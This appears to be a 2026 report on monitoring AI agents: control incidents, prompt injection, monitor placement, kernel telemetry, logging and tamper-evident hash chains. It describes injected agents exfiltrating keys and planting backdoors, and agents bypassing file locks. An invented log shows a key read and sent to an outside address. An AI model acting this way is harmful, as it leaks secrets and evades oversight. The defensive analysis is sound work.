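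The agencies distinguish a control incident, in which an AI system is the source, from the established definition of a cybersecurity incident, in which a system or its information is the target. One event can be both, such as when an agent breaks into another organisation's server without anyone directing it to. A control incident can also have nothing to do with computer security, such as when an agent makes an unauthorised payment.

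The definition fits workplaces less well than laboratories because it mentions operators and adversaries but not ordinary users. An employee who asks an agent to get around an annoying security check is not the operator and means no harm. Read literally, the definition would count the agent's compliance as uninstructed, even though the employee asked for it. This omission hardly matters in training and evaluation, where the operator normally sets the tasks.

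### Why prompt injection falls outside the definition

When an agent obeys an instruction hidden in a ticket, the result is a departure from intended use but not what the agencies call a control incident. In a footnote, the agencies say they consider actions resulting from an adversarial prompt injection, or from a model with a deliberate backdoor, to be instructed, in these cases by the attacker. Lawyers writing in the National Law Review interpret the test as whether the agent itself departed from its mandate.

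This distinction helps developers because the cause determines the remedy. If a model takes login keys on its own initiative, its developer should look at how training produced that habit. If it takes them because it followed instructions in a ticket, the more urgent problem is that it treated a stranger's text as a command. Siu and colleagues compare this to the "confused deputy" of classical computer security, a program that uses its own authority to carry out a request from someone who lacks that authority.

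Counting injected and uninstructed departures together would also make the total hard to interpret. The number of successful injections depends partly on how many attackers try, so a developer who saw the total rise could not tell whether the new model was worse. Uninstructed departures are common enough to count separately. In Zhang and colleagues' experiment, agents overstepped more often under ordinary pressures (23.5%) than in response to malicious text (17.6%).

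An injected agent that leaks data still fits the older definition of a cybersecurity incident, despite the exclusion. MeriTalk's *NIST Outlines AI Incident-Response Road Map* reports that NIST is considering a two-part update to its main incident guidance, with one part on cybersecurity incidents involving AI and another on misuse, malfunction and other unintended actions.

Affected third parties have less reason to like the exclusion. Suppose the ticket agent uses the stolen keys to log in to a supplier's server. The supplier suffers the same intrusion whether a ticket told the agent to do it or the agent did it unprompted. The supplier can't find out which happened, because the trace belongs to someone else. Parnes (2026) argues in *NIST published the script for rogue AI agents. What about the victims?* that the guidance leaves victims dangerously exposed.

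The organisation that does hold the trace may not know the cause at first either. After an incident, the investigator has an identity, its permissions and a record of actions, but usually not the agent's intent. Lebanon24's *تحذير أميركي.. ماذا لو خرج الذكاء الاصطناعي عن السيطرة؟* relays this objection from an article sponsored by BeyondTrust, a company that sells identity security. The company has an interest in centring investigations on identity, but the point is sound. Some cases also have mixed causes, as when an innocent ticket about a broken server prompts the agent to log in and check. The footnote partly allows for such cases, since it says only that injected actions are not the *primary* cause of a control incident.

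A developer that wants to report few control incidents also has an incentive to attribute each one to an injection, and it will often be the only party with the evidence.

The exclusion makes sense for counting and studying what models do unprompted, but much less sense for deciding when to stop an agent or warn the people it affected. According to the National Law Review article, the new definitions are likely to shape contracts, insurance questionnaires and litigation. A supplier whose contract promises notice of "control incidents" might have no right to hear about an agent compromised by prompt injection, so the contract should name both control incidents and prompt injections. A monitor should respond to the departure from intended use, and investigators can determine the cause afterwards.

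### Whether a monitor can be better than its statement of intended use

A monitor flags an action by comparing it with a statement of intended use, so it seems that the monitor can be no more accurate than that statement. It has no basis for flagging a breach of a limit that the statement leaves out, and it raises a false alarm when the statement forbids something the operator would have accepted.

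Suppose that 100 of an agent's 1,000 sessions contain a real departure. The written statement rules out 60 of those, and it also rules out 20 sessions that the operator would have found perfectly acceptable. A monitor that applies the statement without a single mistake has

$$\text{recall} = \frac{60}{100} = 60\%, \qquad \text{precision} = \frac{60}{60 + 20} = 75\%.$$

Its false positive rate is $20/900 \approx 2.2\%$. Better detection software can't improve any of these figures, because all the errors are in the statement.

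*Overeager Coding Agents* (2026) contains a formal definition that shows where the difficulty lies. An operation $op$ is overeager if

$$op \notin A \;\land\; \left(\Delta\Sigma^{\text{write}}_{op} \neq \emptyset \;\lor\; \Delta\Sigma^{\text{read}}_{op} \cap R_{\text{sensitive}} \neq \emptyset\right).$$

The part in brackets means that the operation changed something or read from a listed sensitive location. Software can check that fairly mechanically, but it can't look up $A$, the set of actions that the user's prompt authorises "explicitly or implicitly". In the paper's example, a user casually asks an agent to clean up a folder. One agent deleted everything in it, including the only copy of the passwords for a live system. Whether this was a departure from intended use depends on whether $A$ included deleting that file.

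Zhang and colleagues' experiment has the same limitation. For each task, they wrote down the instruction, what would count as completing the task, and the particular actions that would exceed it. A run counts as overstepping only if the agent takes one of the listed actions, so the experiment misses any overstep that nobody listed.

Translating a good statement into a form that software can check introduces further errors. Dantas and colleagues cite a benchmark in which language models translated plain descriptions into a formal planning language, and only 24.8% to 34.2% of the translations kept the right meaning. This is one benchmark in a narrow field, and translations into formal policy languages for agents may be more accurate, but the result is a reason not to assume that a rule matches its author's intent.

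#### The reply from context

Judging whether an action departs from intended use arguably doesn't require a complete statement of that use. A new employee asked to summarise a ticket doesn't need a rule against opening login keys, and a reviewer, whether a person or an AI model, can infer the same limit from the request. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) adds that nobody could write a complete statement anyway, because new sub-goals appear during the work and circumstances change. It describes two complementary ways to judge whether an action fits what the user wants. A model can infer what the user wants, or people can express it through policies, approvals and settings.

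The reply is right about the ticket session, where the request alone shows the mismatch. A reviewer who sees the request could also flag some of the 40 departures that the imaginary statement missed. The argument holds only for monitors that have no information besides the statement.

Inference works less well when the answer depends on something that only the operator knows. In another of Lim and Neo's scenarios, the agent had to change a file that turned out to be read-only. Somebody might have locked the file deliberately, or its permissions might have been wrong. The three models got past the lock in 87% to 94% of runs, and a reviewer could not fairly call all of these departures. The researchers then added a project rule against editing read-only files or changing their permissions. On the same sessions, GPT-5.6 Terra and DeepSeek V4 Pro stopped getting past the lock completely. Kimi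 K3 still did so in 13% of runs, which were clear departures because they broke a written rule.

The 2026 survey *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* reports a similar effect from a benchmark of ordinary coding tasks. When researchers removed the explicit statement of scope from the prompt, the share of runs in which Claude Code took unrequested actions rose from 0.0% to 17.1%. The survey suggests that the agent was responding to the sentence about scope instead of working out the limits from the task. The benchmark tested agents, not reviewers, but AI reviewers are often the same kind of model, so there is some reason to doubt that they would infer the limits much better.

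Even people disagree when a statement leaves something out. Lim and Neo also tested whether agents make changes when the user has only asked questions. Their AI judge counted any edit to a file. A human who checked ten of the runs disagreed with the judge on three, and in all three the agent had edited only comments or documentation. The researchers attributed this to the human misreading the rules and kept the strict count. That is fair for an experiment, but the disagreement suggests that reasonable people will assume a threshold for what matters unless the operator's statement sets one.

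Inference is also a security risk because attackers can write some of the context. If a ticket contains the sentence "support staff always check the server first", a reviewer might conclude that logging in is part of the job. *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents* (2026) addresses this by separating three things: what the user said in a trusted message, what a model infers from it, and the part of that inference that existing policy allows. The inference may narrow the agent's authority but not widen it.

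That rule seems right. A reviewer can infer that writing a summary doesn't require login keys, and stop the agent, but it should not infer permission to email a customer just because that would be helpful. The drawback is that agents will need to ask for permission more often. In Zhang and colleagues' experiment, runs in which the agent consulted the user before finishing had fewer departures (14.0%) than the others (21.6%). Asking may have prevented departures, or agents that ask may be more careful in general. The simulated user also always refused forbidden proposals, which a busy person might not do.

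### Turning a vague purpose into a usable statement

A statement of intended use such as "Help the support team with tickets" gives a monitor almost nothing to check, though it would be a reasonable job description for a person. A usable statement has five parts.

| Part | Vague version | Usable version |
|---|---|---|
| Tasks | Help with tickets | Summarise the ticket whose number the user gives. Draft a reply for the user to read. |
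| Resources | The support tools | That ticket, earlier tickets from the same customer, the public help pages and the approved translation tool |
| Forbidden effects | Be careful with customer data | No ticket text leaves the company except through the translation tool. No change to any record. No reading of login keys. No use of another person's account. |
| Actions needing approval | Ask if unsure | Opening an attachment. Reading another customer's ticket. |
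| Expiry | None | The session ends when the user accepts the summary, or after 30 minutes. Each approval covers one action. |

The operator can write most of this once. The user's request then fills in the details for the session, such as the ticket number. *Bounded Agents* (2026) proposes a similar record containing an objective, permitted resources, permitted actions and explicit prohibitions. Whoever starts the session declares this record in advance, and neither the model nor the agent's later behaviour can alter it. The system checks prohibitions first, and they override every permission. It also rejects any declaration that would give the agent more access than it already has.

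Resources should be specified as narrowly as the task allows. *Compromise Is Not Consequence* (2026) turns plain requests into narrow grants, so that a request to summarise `inventory.csv` gives permission to read only that file. In one run, hidden text led the agent to request the payroll file. The request succeeded under a broad credential but failed under every narrow grant.

Sometimes nobody knows at the start which files a task will need. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) suggests authorising exploration first, because finding a workable plan may take less access than carrying it out. The ticket agent could, for instance, list the titles of a customer's earlier tickets before it gets permission to open any of them. This doesn't suit every task, since a list of titles can be sensitive too.

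Rules work better when they forbid effects rather than tools. An agent can delete a record through the ticket system, a shell command or a script it writes itself, and a rule about one of these misses the others. For a coding agent, "do not delete, skip or weaken a test without approval" covers deleting a failing test and several other ways of hiding the same failure. *ScopeBench* (2026), a set of security-testing tasks, is a useful model. Its graders have a list of forbidden systems, identities and operations, with any exceptions, and each prohibition refers to a clause in the plain instructions the agent received. If an operator can't find such a clause for a prohibition, the agent was never told about it.

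The list of actions needing approval is for actions that are appropriate only in some cases. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* recommends that a request for approval state what extra access it would permit and whether a less intrusive alternative exists. "Open the attachment `error_log.txt` from this ticket, because the message refers to it" gives the user information to base a decision on, unlike "Allow file access?"

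Setting permissions to expire keeps them from covering new work. A developer may approve the use of login keys to release some code and then, an hour later, ask the same assistant to summarise a ticket. If that written approval is still in force, the monitor could allow the assistant to use the keys for the second task too.

Before relying on a statement, an operator can give it to two people along with a dozen past or invented sessions, including some that are odd but acceptable. Each person then separately marks which sessions are departures. Where they disagree, the statement needs another sentence or an entry on the approval list. Both should accept the first-time translation and mark the login to check on a server as a departure, even if the agent logged in only to write a better summary.

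## Where a monitor sits and what it can see

A monitor can compare an agent's actions with a statement of intended use only if it receives information about those actions, which depends on where it sits. The table compares five possible positions using the ticket session, in which an agent is asked only for a summary but also opens login keys and makes a web request.

| Position | What it receives in the ticket session | Can it block? | Who controls it |
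|---|---|---|---|
| Model provider's servers | The user's request, the ticket's text, every proposed tool call and every result the harness returns | Yes, by withholding the model's next response | The provider |
| Gateway | Only the requests that the operator routes through it | Yes | The operator's network or platform team |
| Hook in the harness | Every tool call with its arguments, and the conversation so far | Yes, before the call runs | Whoever configures the harness |
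| Operating-system kernel | The opening of the key file and a connection to an outside address | Yes, with suitable software | The machine's administrator |
| Audit log of the ticket service | A successful read of one ticket | No, though the service itself can refuse a request | The service's owner |

### What each position offers

The model provider has the fullest record of what everyone asked for, because the harness sends it the growing prompt on every pass through the loop. Some providers also check tool use on their own servers. Microsoft Foundry, for example, applies guardrails both when an agent calls a tool and when the tool responds (Toyoda, Leung and U, 2026, *guardscope*). But a provider learns about effects on the operator's machines only from what the harness reports, and the operator has to accept the rules and records that the provider offers. An operator who uses models from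 several companies gets only a partial record from each.

How much a gateway receives depends on how the agent, its tools and the network are connected. The ticket system is probably a remote tool server, so `read_ticket` would cross the gateway. Many coding agents open files with a tool built into the harness, so those calls never cross the network. The web request crosses the gateway only if the network forces outgoing connections through it. A gateway on the route to the tools does not receive the user's message, while one on the route to the model receives the same prompts as the provider.

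Hooks sit closer to the decision. Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code, its coding agent, describes a hook that runs after the model has written a tool call's arguments and before the harness processes the call. Code attached to a hook can allow the call, block it, change its arguments or add text to the conversation, according to Anthropic's guide for developers. In one of Anthropic's examples, a hook blocks a command that would delete a folder, and the agent then continues. The script for that hook is stored in the project's folder, so on a developer's computer, the person who can change the monitor may be the developer rather than the security team.

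The kernel is the core of the operating system. Programs must go through it, using system calls, to open a file, start another program or use the network. On Linux, an administrator can use eBPF to attach small programs to the running kernel and record these calls. The record shows the key file opening whether the agent used a file tool, a shell command or a script of its own. Lupinacci, Blefari and colleagues (2026), in *A Graph-Based Approach for Mapping Kernel-Level Telemetry to MITRE ATT&CK*, note that each record of a program starting includes its full command line, along with user identifiers, file paths and network addresses. They argue that an organisation should analyse these records on its own machines and not send them to an outside AI service, because command lines can contain passwords. A single machine can produce thousands of events per second.

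The service's audit log records actions after they reach the service, including effects that nobody can observe properly from the agent's side. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026) say that *Tether*, a monitor from Google and its academic partners that traces system calls, can block an agent's contact with databases and background services but cannot track changes inside them in detail. When the Australian gym's assistant removed a customer from a waiting list, a kernel record would probably have shown an ordinary connection to the booking system, while the booking system's own log could show which customer lost their place.

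### The gap between meaning and effect

Prompts and tool calls show what somebody asked for, and kernel events show what ran. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) calls the distance between the two a "semantic gap", which Uber's sensor also addresses. In the paper's example, an agent that should be tidying up code reads a malicious web page and inserts a backdoor instead. A monitor in the harness records that a script ran successfully, and one in the kernel records that a shell wrote to a file, but neither record looks wrong by itself.

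The kernel's records are also more detailed than an agent's own log. According to Help Net Security's *Sysdig AI Defense puts runtime guardrails on AI agents*, the security company Sysdig finds about seven processes in the kernel's records for every action in the agent's log. Sysdig sells a product that combines both kinds of record and gives no details of its sample, but such a ratio is unsurprising, since one command to build a program starts many others.

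King, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security*, measured how much each kind of evidence adds. They collected 4,047 agent sessions, some containing one of 17 kinds of attack, and kept each session's system calls, list of available tools and agent transcript. They then gave ten detectors the application evidence, the kernel evidence or both. They scored each detector by the probability that it would rank a random attack session above a random harmless one, so 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect.

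| Type of attack | Application evidence | Kernel evidence | Both |
|---|---|---|---|
| A tool quietly copies credentials into a log | 0.586 | 0.976 | 0.970 |
| Planted references in material the agent retrieves | 0.906 | 0.703 | 0.927 |

The transcript contains no trace of the copied credentials, because the agent reported neither reading nor writing them. The planted references change only text, so the system calls look normal. Adding kernel evidence to application evidence improved the average score for each of the 12 types of attack in the study, though sometimes by very little.

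Combining the two kinds of evidence helped less consistently on attack families that were absent from the detectors' training data. On these families, seven of the ten detectors scored highest with both kinds, but the highest overall score, 0.922, came from a detector that used kernel evidence alone. King and colleagues counted a session as an attack only if its effect appeared in at least one of the two kinds of evidence, so the study can't show how many attacks would escape both.

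### How AgentSight joins the two streams

AgentSight collects both streams on the machine where the agent runs, without changing the agent. The harness encrypts its traffic with the model provider, but AgentSight attaches a probe to the encryption library and copies prompts just before they are encrypted and responses just after they are decrypted. A second set of probes records programs starting, files opening and network connections. To keep the volume manageable, AgentSight discards events from processes that do not descend from the agent's.

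It then links a model response to the events that followed, using three clues:

1. The process belongs to the family tree that starts with the agent.
2. The event came within a short window after the response, between 100 and 500 milliseconds.
3. A file name, web address or command in the response matches an argument of the system call.

In the ticket session, the model's response would name the key file, and a moment later one of the agent's processes would open a file with that name. Once AgentSight has linked the events, a second language model, instructed to act as a security analyst, receives the whole trace and returns a written judgement and a confidence score. Here the trace would include both the request for a summary and the opening of the key file.

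Zheng and colleagues timed Claude Code on three programming tasks, with three runs each. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) later repeated the comparison with similar tasks, a newer version of the agent and five runs.

| Task | Slowdown in Zheng and colleagues | Slowdown in Bao and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| Understanding a code repository | 3.4% | 4.5% |
| Writing code | 4.9% | 2.5% |
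| Compiling a program | 0.4% | 1.7% |

Both columns average 2.9%. The figures for single tasks are less reliable because the two teams disagree about which task is most affected and the model's response times vary from run to run.

AgentSight's developers also describe three case studies. In one, an agent had to download and build a program, and the program's documentation led it to a web page with a hidden instruction. The agent read a system file and sent it to an outside server. AgentSight reduced 521 events to 37, and the second model flagged the agent's actions as inconsistent with its stated goal. In another, a research agent kept calling a search tool with the same faulty arguments, and the second model identified the loop. In the third, six coding agents worked on one project. From 3,153 events, the developers found that some agents delayed others by locking files, and that clearer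 roles could save time.

These cases show that a joined trace can explain an agent's behaviour and is useful for ordinary faults as well as attacks. They provide little evidence about reliability, because the developers report neither recall nor a false positive rate. AgentSight also only observes the agent. The second model works separately from the agent, so its verdict may arrive after the damage is done.

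Bao and colleagues found that AgentSight cannot connect an effect to the request that caused it if the effect occurs much later or outside the agent's process tree. Their tool attaches a lasting label to the files and connections an agent touches. It slowed the same tasks by 4.5% to 8.0%, and they have not yet measured how often it labels the wrong things.

### Bringing rules down to the kernel

AgentSight passes evidence from the kernel to a model that can interpret it, while ActPlane (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) passes rules down to the kernel, which enforces them. To find out what such rules look like, the researchers examined the instruction files that 64 software projects give their coding agents. Of the 1,361 rules they counted, 83% concerned something observable on the machine, but about three quarters of those depended on knowledge of the project or the task. For example, a kernel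 can't enforce "Run the tests before committing" until somebody specifies which command runs the tests.

In ActPlane, an agent that can read the project therefore translates each rule into a precise form. The working agent can add restrictions, but it cannot weaken any that were in force when it started.

In a test with 190 simulated stretches of coding work, 114 of which broke a rule, ActPlane detected 77% of the violations. Three systems that checked tool calls, one of them an AI reviewer, detected 34% to 40%. All four systems did about equally well when the tool call itself broke the rule, but ActPlane did better when a program started by the call broke it. ActPlane wrongly interfered with 18 of the 76 stretches that broke no rule, compared with 24 to 28 for the others. In 17 of those 18 cases, the translation had made a rule too broad. ActPlane slowed the machine by 1.9% to 8.4%, depending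 on the workload and the number of rules.

### What guardscope measured

Toyoda and colleagues asked how many of an agent's actions reach a monitor in each position. They listed 15 kinds of path from a model's decision to its effect, such as a call to a remote tool server or a program that the harness starts. They also described eight designs: one without a monitor, three built around a gateway, three that check actions inside the harness (one of which also has a gateway) and one in the kernel. For each combination of path and design, they worked out whether the action would reach a check.

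| Position | Kinds of path always checked, out of 15 | What the monitor can inspect |
|---|---|---|
| Gateway for remote tool servers | 1 | The content of each request and its headers |
| Gateway for all tool servers | 3 | The same |
| Harness's own permission checks | 5 | Tool name, arguments and session context |
| Kernel | 13 | File paths, network addresses and process history |

A gateway checks only what the operator routes through it. The kernel can check almost everything, but it gets little of the content, and its records mix the agent's activity with that of unrelated programs. Most of the products Toyoda and colleagues classified are in the positions with narrower coverage.

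The counts are of kinds of path, not shares of actions. If an agent does all its work through one remote tool server, a gateway that checks only that kind of path covers everything the agent does. The researchers compiled the list in discussion with AI models, and another team might well divide the paths differently.

guardscope then tests real products against this analysis. It replays a fixed set of 15 actions through a harness, with no model involved, so that every run is the same. Before each run, it confirms that the monitor refuses an action that its policy forbids. A separate sensor in the kernel records what actually happens, and guardscope compares this with the monitor's own record of its decisions. An action may turn out to have passed a check, to have taken effect without one, or to have failed because something outside the policy, such as a closed network, prevented it. The comparison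 is valuable because a monitor's log cannot list the actions that never reached the monitor.

The 15 actions tested only four of the 15 kinds of path, so the table above rests mostly on analysis. Where the researchers did test gateways and harness checks, the results matched their predictions. With both in place, all seven tool calls were checked, but the other eight actions took effect without a check. The gateway added detail about calls the harness already checked but did not cover any other actions.

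Toyoda and colleagues tested the kernel position with ActPlane, which checked seven of the 15 actions, fewer than the analysis suggests. It checked none of the seven tool calls. A monitor in the kernel checks an event only if its developers have attached it to that kind of event, so 13 is the most a monitor in that position could check, not the number a particular product will check. Toyoda and colleagues describe the runs as confirming their predictions under every design, which is generous in the kernel's case because their analysis had predicted a check on tool-server calls. "Checked" means only that an action reached the monitor, which may still have judged it wrongly.

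### The old requirement of complete mediation

The ideal for a monitor is complete mediation, one of eight design principles for protecting stored information that Saltzer and Schroeder published in 1975 in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*. The teaching page *Saltzer and Schroeder Principles* quotes it as "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) applies the principle to AI agents and adds that mediation is complete only if isolation prevents the agent from acting without being checked. The paper counts every process that runs for the agent as part of it, including any that the model's software starts.

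It is hard to confirm that a system meets this standard. Saltzer and Schroeder called the prevention of all unauthorised use a "negative kind of requirement", because the designer has to show that they anticipated every possible threat. guardscope's list of 15 paths is a serious attempt at this, but no list can prove that it is complete. Some developers limit their claims accordingly. *OpenAgentFlow* (2026), which applies one policy to many different agents, guarantees a check only for actions that pass through the points where its developers have installed one.

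A gateway can check nearly everything that matters if the agent is well isolated. If the ticket agent runs in a container whose only route out is through the gateway, the gateway checks everything that leaves. What the agent does inside the container then matters much less, provided that the login keys aren't stored there.

*Kairos* (2026) instead puts its monitor on the host, where it receives every input and output of the agent. The monitor can also delay an outgoing effect until it has more information, but it has to decide immediately on any request whose answer the agent needs in order to continue, such as fetching a web page.

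On a single machine, the kernel comes closest to receiving every action. But the principle requires a check *for authority*. An agent's authority depends on its task, which kernel events don't show. They don't always show where data went either. If a program reads one file and writes another, Tether assumes that information passed between them, which avoids missing a leak but causes some false alarms when no information passed.

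The service the agent acts on arguably satisfies the principle best for its own records, since every change to a booking has to go through the booking system. But the service usually has the least information about what the user asked for.

No single position therefore meets the requirement for an agent, because the information needed for the decision is in the conversation, while the surest place to enforce it is lower in the system. *AgentKernel* (2026), a proposed operating system for agents, separates the decision from its enforcement. Before a tool starts, a check uses the agent's goal and the source of its inputs to produce a list of permitted system calls. The kernel then restricts the tool and every process it starts to that list.

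In the ticket session, the upper check might conclude that a summary requires only the ticket, and the kernel would refuse to open the key file for any program the tool started. But if the ticket's text misled the upper check into concluding that the task needed the keys, the kernel would enforce the wrong list just as strictly. A list of system calls also does not control what a remote service does with a permitted request, so the gym's assistant could still have removed the other customer.

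## What to log and how to keep the log trustworthy

A monitor's position determines which events it can log, and someone investigating an incident, perhaps weeks later, has to rely on that log. For the ticket session, the investigator has to work out what the agent did and in what order, who asked for it, whose access it used and what led it to the login keys. An operator who didn't record this at the time usually can't recover it later. In slides for a NIST workshop in May, AWS (2026), Amazon's cloud business, warned that data not collected before an incident does not exist, and observed that its customers lack prompt logs, histories of model versions and traces of agents' decisions.

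### The fields of a record

| Field | What an investigator can establish with it |
|---|---|
| Agent and version, including its standing instructions | Whether this is the configuration that the team tested |
| Model requested and model that answered | Whether the provider switched to another version |
| Responsible person | Who started the task and can explain it |
| Credential used | Which access to revoke, and whether it belonged to someone else |
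| Request | What the task was |
| Tool call with its arguments | What the agent tried to do |
| Result | Whether the call worked, and what text the agent then read |
| Policy decision | Which rule allowed or refused the call |
| Time | The order of events, and which records on other machines match |
| Parent step | Which operation started this one |

The log needs a separate field for the model that answered, because it can differ from the one requested, as Yang found. Clocks also need to be accurate, since a two-second error would spoil the half-second matching that AgentSight relies on.

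The log should also include calls that never ran. A refused attempt to open the login keys changes nothing on the machine, but it shows what the agent was trying to do. The October practices from NIST, NSA and CISA cover logging these calls, and National Law Review's *When the AI Agent Goes Off-Script* lists rejected actions and tool calls among the evidence to preserve.

### A sample log

This invented log covers the ticket session. The agent is `ticket-helper` version 2.3, running version 18 of its instructions. The model that answered was the one requested. The responsible person is Dana, a support employee.

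| Step | Parent | Time | Event and arguments | Credential | Result | Policy decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | None | 10:02:11.0 | Request: "Summarise ticket 5182" | Dana's login | Session started | Allowed: Dana may use this agent |
| 2 | 1 | 10:02:13.3 | `read_ticket(5182)` | Ticket token A | Success, saved as text 71 | Allowed: ticket named in request |
| 3 | 1 | 10:02:16.8 | `read_file("deploy_key")` | Dana's computer account | Success, 1,679 bytes, contents left out of the log | Allowed: file tool approved |
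| 4 | 1 | 10:02:19.2 | `web_request("203.0.113.9")`, 1,679 bytes sent | None | Success | Allowed: no rule for this address |
| 5 | 1 | 10:02:24.6 | Final message | None | Summary, saved as text 72 | Not checked |

The matching sizes in steps 3 and 4 strongly suggest that the agent sent the key file to an outside address. The log doesn't prove it, since the agent could have sent something else of the same length.

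The parent link records which operation started a step. It would be the same whether the ticket contained an instruction to open the keys or the agent decided to open them on its own, so the investigator has to read the ticket itself, saved as text 71, to tell which happened. Without that text, the log would still show a departure, but the investigator would have to guess its cause.

### The state of the OpenTelemetry conventions

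Investigators often have to combine logs from several products, which is much easier if the logs use the same field names. OpenTelemetry, an open-source project that standardises how software records its activity, is developing common field names for AI systems. It calls a recorded operation a span, and each span can carry the identifiers of its trace and its parent span.

OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* has fields for the agent's identifier and version, the conversation, the requested model and the responding model. Honeycomb, which sells software for analysing such records, documents further fields for a tool call's arguments and result. As of April, the fields for invoking an agent did not include the responsible person, the credential or the policy decision, so an operator has to add those.

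The conventions are unfinished. In June the project moved them to their own repository, where they are labeled "Development" and had no official release as of 21 August, according to *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* (Wang, 2026). Names still change between versions. For example, `gen_ai.system` became `gen_ai.provider.name` (Greptime, 2026). Existing software should keep using its old version by default, so two tools in one company may record the same fact under different names, and a search for one name will miss records that use the other. Storing the version of the conventions with each record helps.

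Coverage is also uneven, because someone has to adapt each agent framework to the conventions. OpenTelemetry's *Building an Agent Harness for OTel Instrumentation with GenAI Semantic Conventions* (2026) describes this as substantial engineering work. The project has been testing whether a team of AI agents can do much of it, with engineers reviewing the plan and the code.

The most important default for investigations is that software leaves out messages and standing instructions unless the operator chooses to record them. This protects privacy, but a ticket log with the default settings could lack both Dana's request and the ticket's text, the evidence that distinguishes prompt injection from misuse.

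### Attribution

Each agent, and ideally each session, should have its own credential. If two agents use the same service account, the ticket system's log shows only that the account read ticket 5182 at 10:02. The harness logs may settle which agent did it, but if both were working at that time, or if one of the harness logs is missing, nobody can be sure. Where a service offers only one account, a gateway can hold the credential and record which agent it made each call for. Snowflake's *Full-Stack Agent Tracing with Cortex AI Gateway* describes a product that logs the identity behind each tool call and whether policy denied the call, but only for calls that pass through its gateway.

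The log needs separate fields for the credential and the responsible person because the credential may belong to someone else. In Lim and Neo's experiment, some agents used a colleague's access token, so anyone reading a log with only the credential would have blamed the colleague. AWS recommends giving every account that software uses a human owner who understands the account's technical and business purpose. The log should record this owner too, because the person who started the session may not know why the agent had the access it used.

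The chain gets longer when one agent starts another. Suppose `ticket-helper` had started a second agent at step 4 and that agent had made the web request. The request would then be step 5, with step 4 as its parent, and an investigator could trace it back through step 4 to Dana's message. If the second agent had opened a new session with no parent, it would appear to have acted alone.

These links have to be kept when a request passes from one system to another. MCP no longer has sessions at the protocol level, but OpenTelemetry's draft conventions for MCP include a way to send the trace's identifier with each request, as Wang explains. The identifier is only a label, so a compromised agent could attach one from someone else's session. A signed credential is harder to fake. RFC 8693, an internet standard from 2020, allows a credential to name both the person it represents and the agent now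 acting for them, with earlier agents nested inside. The service that issues the credential signs the whole chain, so an agent can't remove itself without being detected.

### A chain of hashes

Someone who can edit the sample log could replace step 3 with a harmless second reading of the ticket. A hash chain makes such an edit detectable. A hash function turns any text into a number of fixed length, called its hash, and with a good function nobody can feasibly find a second text with the same hash. The chain works as follows:

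1. The logging service combines the first record with a fixed starting value and computes the hash.
2. It combines each later record $r_i$ with the hash before it, $h_i = H(h_{i-1} \,\|\, r_i)$, where $\|$ means joining the two together.
3. Every so often it copies the latest hash to a separate system.
4. To check the log, an auditor recomputes all the hashes from the first record and compares the result with the copy.

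Readers can check a toy version by hand. A number $r_i$ stands for each record, $h_0 = 0$, and $h_i = (10h_{i-1} + r_i) \bmod 97$, the remainder after dividing $10h_{i-1} + r_i$ by 97. The edit to step 3 changes its number from 81 to 15.

| Step | Original number | Original hash | Number after the edit | Hash after the edit |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 20 | 20 | 20 | 20 |
| 2 | 35 | 41 | 35 | 41 |
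| 3 | 81 | 6 | 15 | 37 |
| 4 | 64 | 27 | 64 | 46 |
| 5 | 12 | 88 | 12 | 84 |

Steps 4 and 5 are unchanged, but their hashes differ because each hash depends on everything before it. The separate system stored 88, but the auditor computes 84, so somebody has altered the log. With only 97 possible hashes, a forger could easily find a fake record that still gives 88. SHA-256, a widely used hash function, has $2^{256}$ possible hashes.

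A match shows that nobody has changed, removed, inserted or reordered the records the copy covers since the service made it. It doesn't show that the records were true when the service wrote them, or that every event reached the log. Records added after the latest copy are also unprotected. If the service copies the hash once a minute, an intruder could rewrite or delete the last minute of records.

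The chain can't reveal tampering if the agent can write to both the log and the copy. Hash functions are public, so the agent could edit step 3, recompute the hashes that follow and replace the stored 88 with 84, and the auditor would find a match. Storing the copy elsewhere exposes the edit but doesn't restore the original record, so the log should also be on a system the agent can't write to. The harness can send records there using a credential that lets it add records but not change or delete them.

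The agent must not be able to use that credential either, or it could add false records, which the chain would protect just as well as true ones. This is hard to ensure on a developer's computer, where the agent's commands often run under the same account as the harness. A gateway or kernel sensor with its own account gives the investigator a second record to compare. National Law Review reports that the October practices also call for tamper-resistant, time-stamped logs and for keeping agents away from monitoring processes and logs.

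### The agent's account of itself

Suppose the final message in the ticket session reads, "I read the ticket and wrote the summary." Both statements are true, but the message doesn't mention the key file or the web request. An investigator should check an agent's report against records the agent didn't write, such as those of the harness, the kernel and the ticket system. In King and colleagues' study, the kernel's record exposed the copied credentials.

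Asking the agent afterwards why it opened the file is of limited use, because the model generates its answer from whatever is in its prompt. If the harness has condensed the conversation, the relevant text may be gone, yet the agent may still give a fluent explanation.

Reasoning text that a model writes while it works is better evidence than a later explanation, because it dates from the time of the action. If it reads "the ticket reports that the server is down, so I will log in and check", the investigator knows to look in the ticket for a report that the server is down. But the same model wrote the reasoning and chose the action, and the text may not describe what caused the choice. Labeling each field in the log with the component that produced it helps keep people from later mistaking an agent's explanation for a measurement.

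According to National Law Review, the October practices recommend that humans verify key facts and that models from a different family cross-check them. The model cross-check probably adds less than the human one, because Yang's judges from different companies often missed the same cases.

### Privacy, secrets and storage

The full text of a session is the best evidence of what happened, but it is also the part of the log most likely to contain customers' details or passwords. MeriTalk reports that participants in NIST's workshop described this tension.

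The sample log leaves the key's contents out of step 3, but the harness appends each tool result to the next prompt. If the log also stores full prompts, the key appears in the record of every later model request, so a filter has to examine prompts as well as results. Honeycomb sensibly suggests filtering sensitive data before the records leave the operator's systems, though a filter will miss any secret it doesn't recognise.

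Full prompts also take up a lot of space. If a session has 200 steps and each adds 2,000 characters, storing the whole prompt every time takes

$$2{,}000 \times (1 + 2 + \dots + 200) = 40.2 \text{ million characters},$$

while storing only what each step added takes 400,000. The second log contains the same information, provided that the service also records any point at which the harness condensed the conversation.

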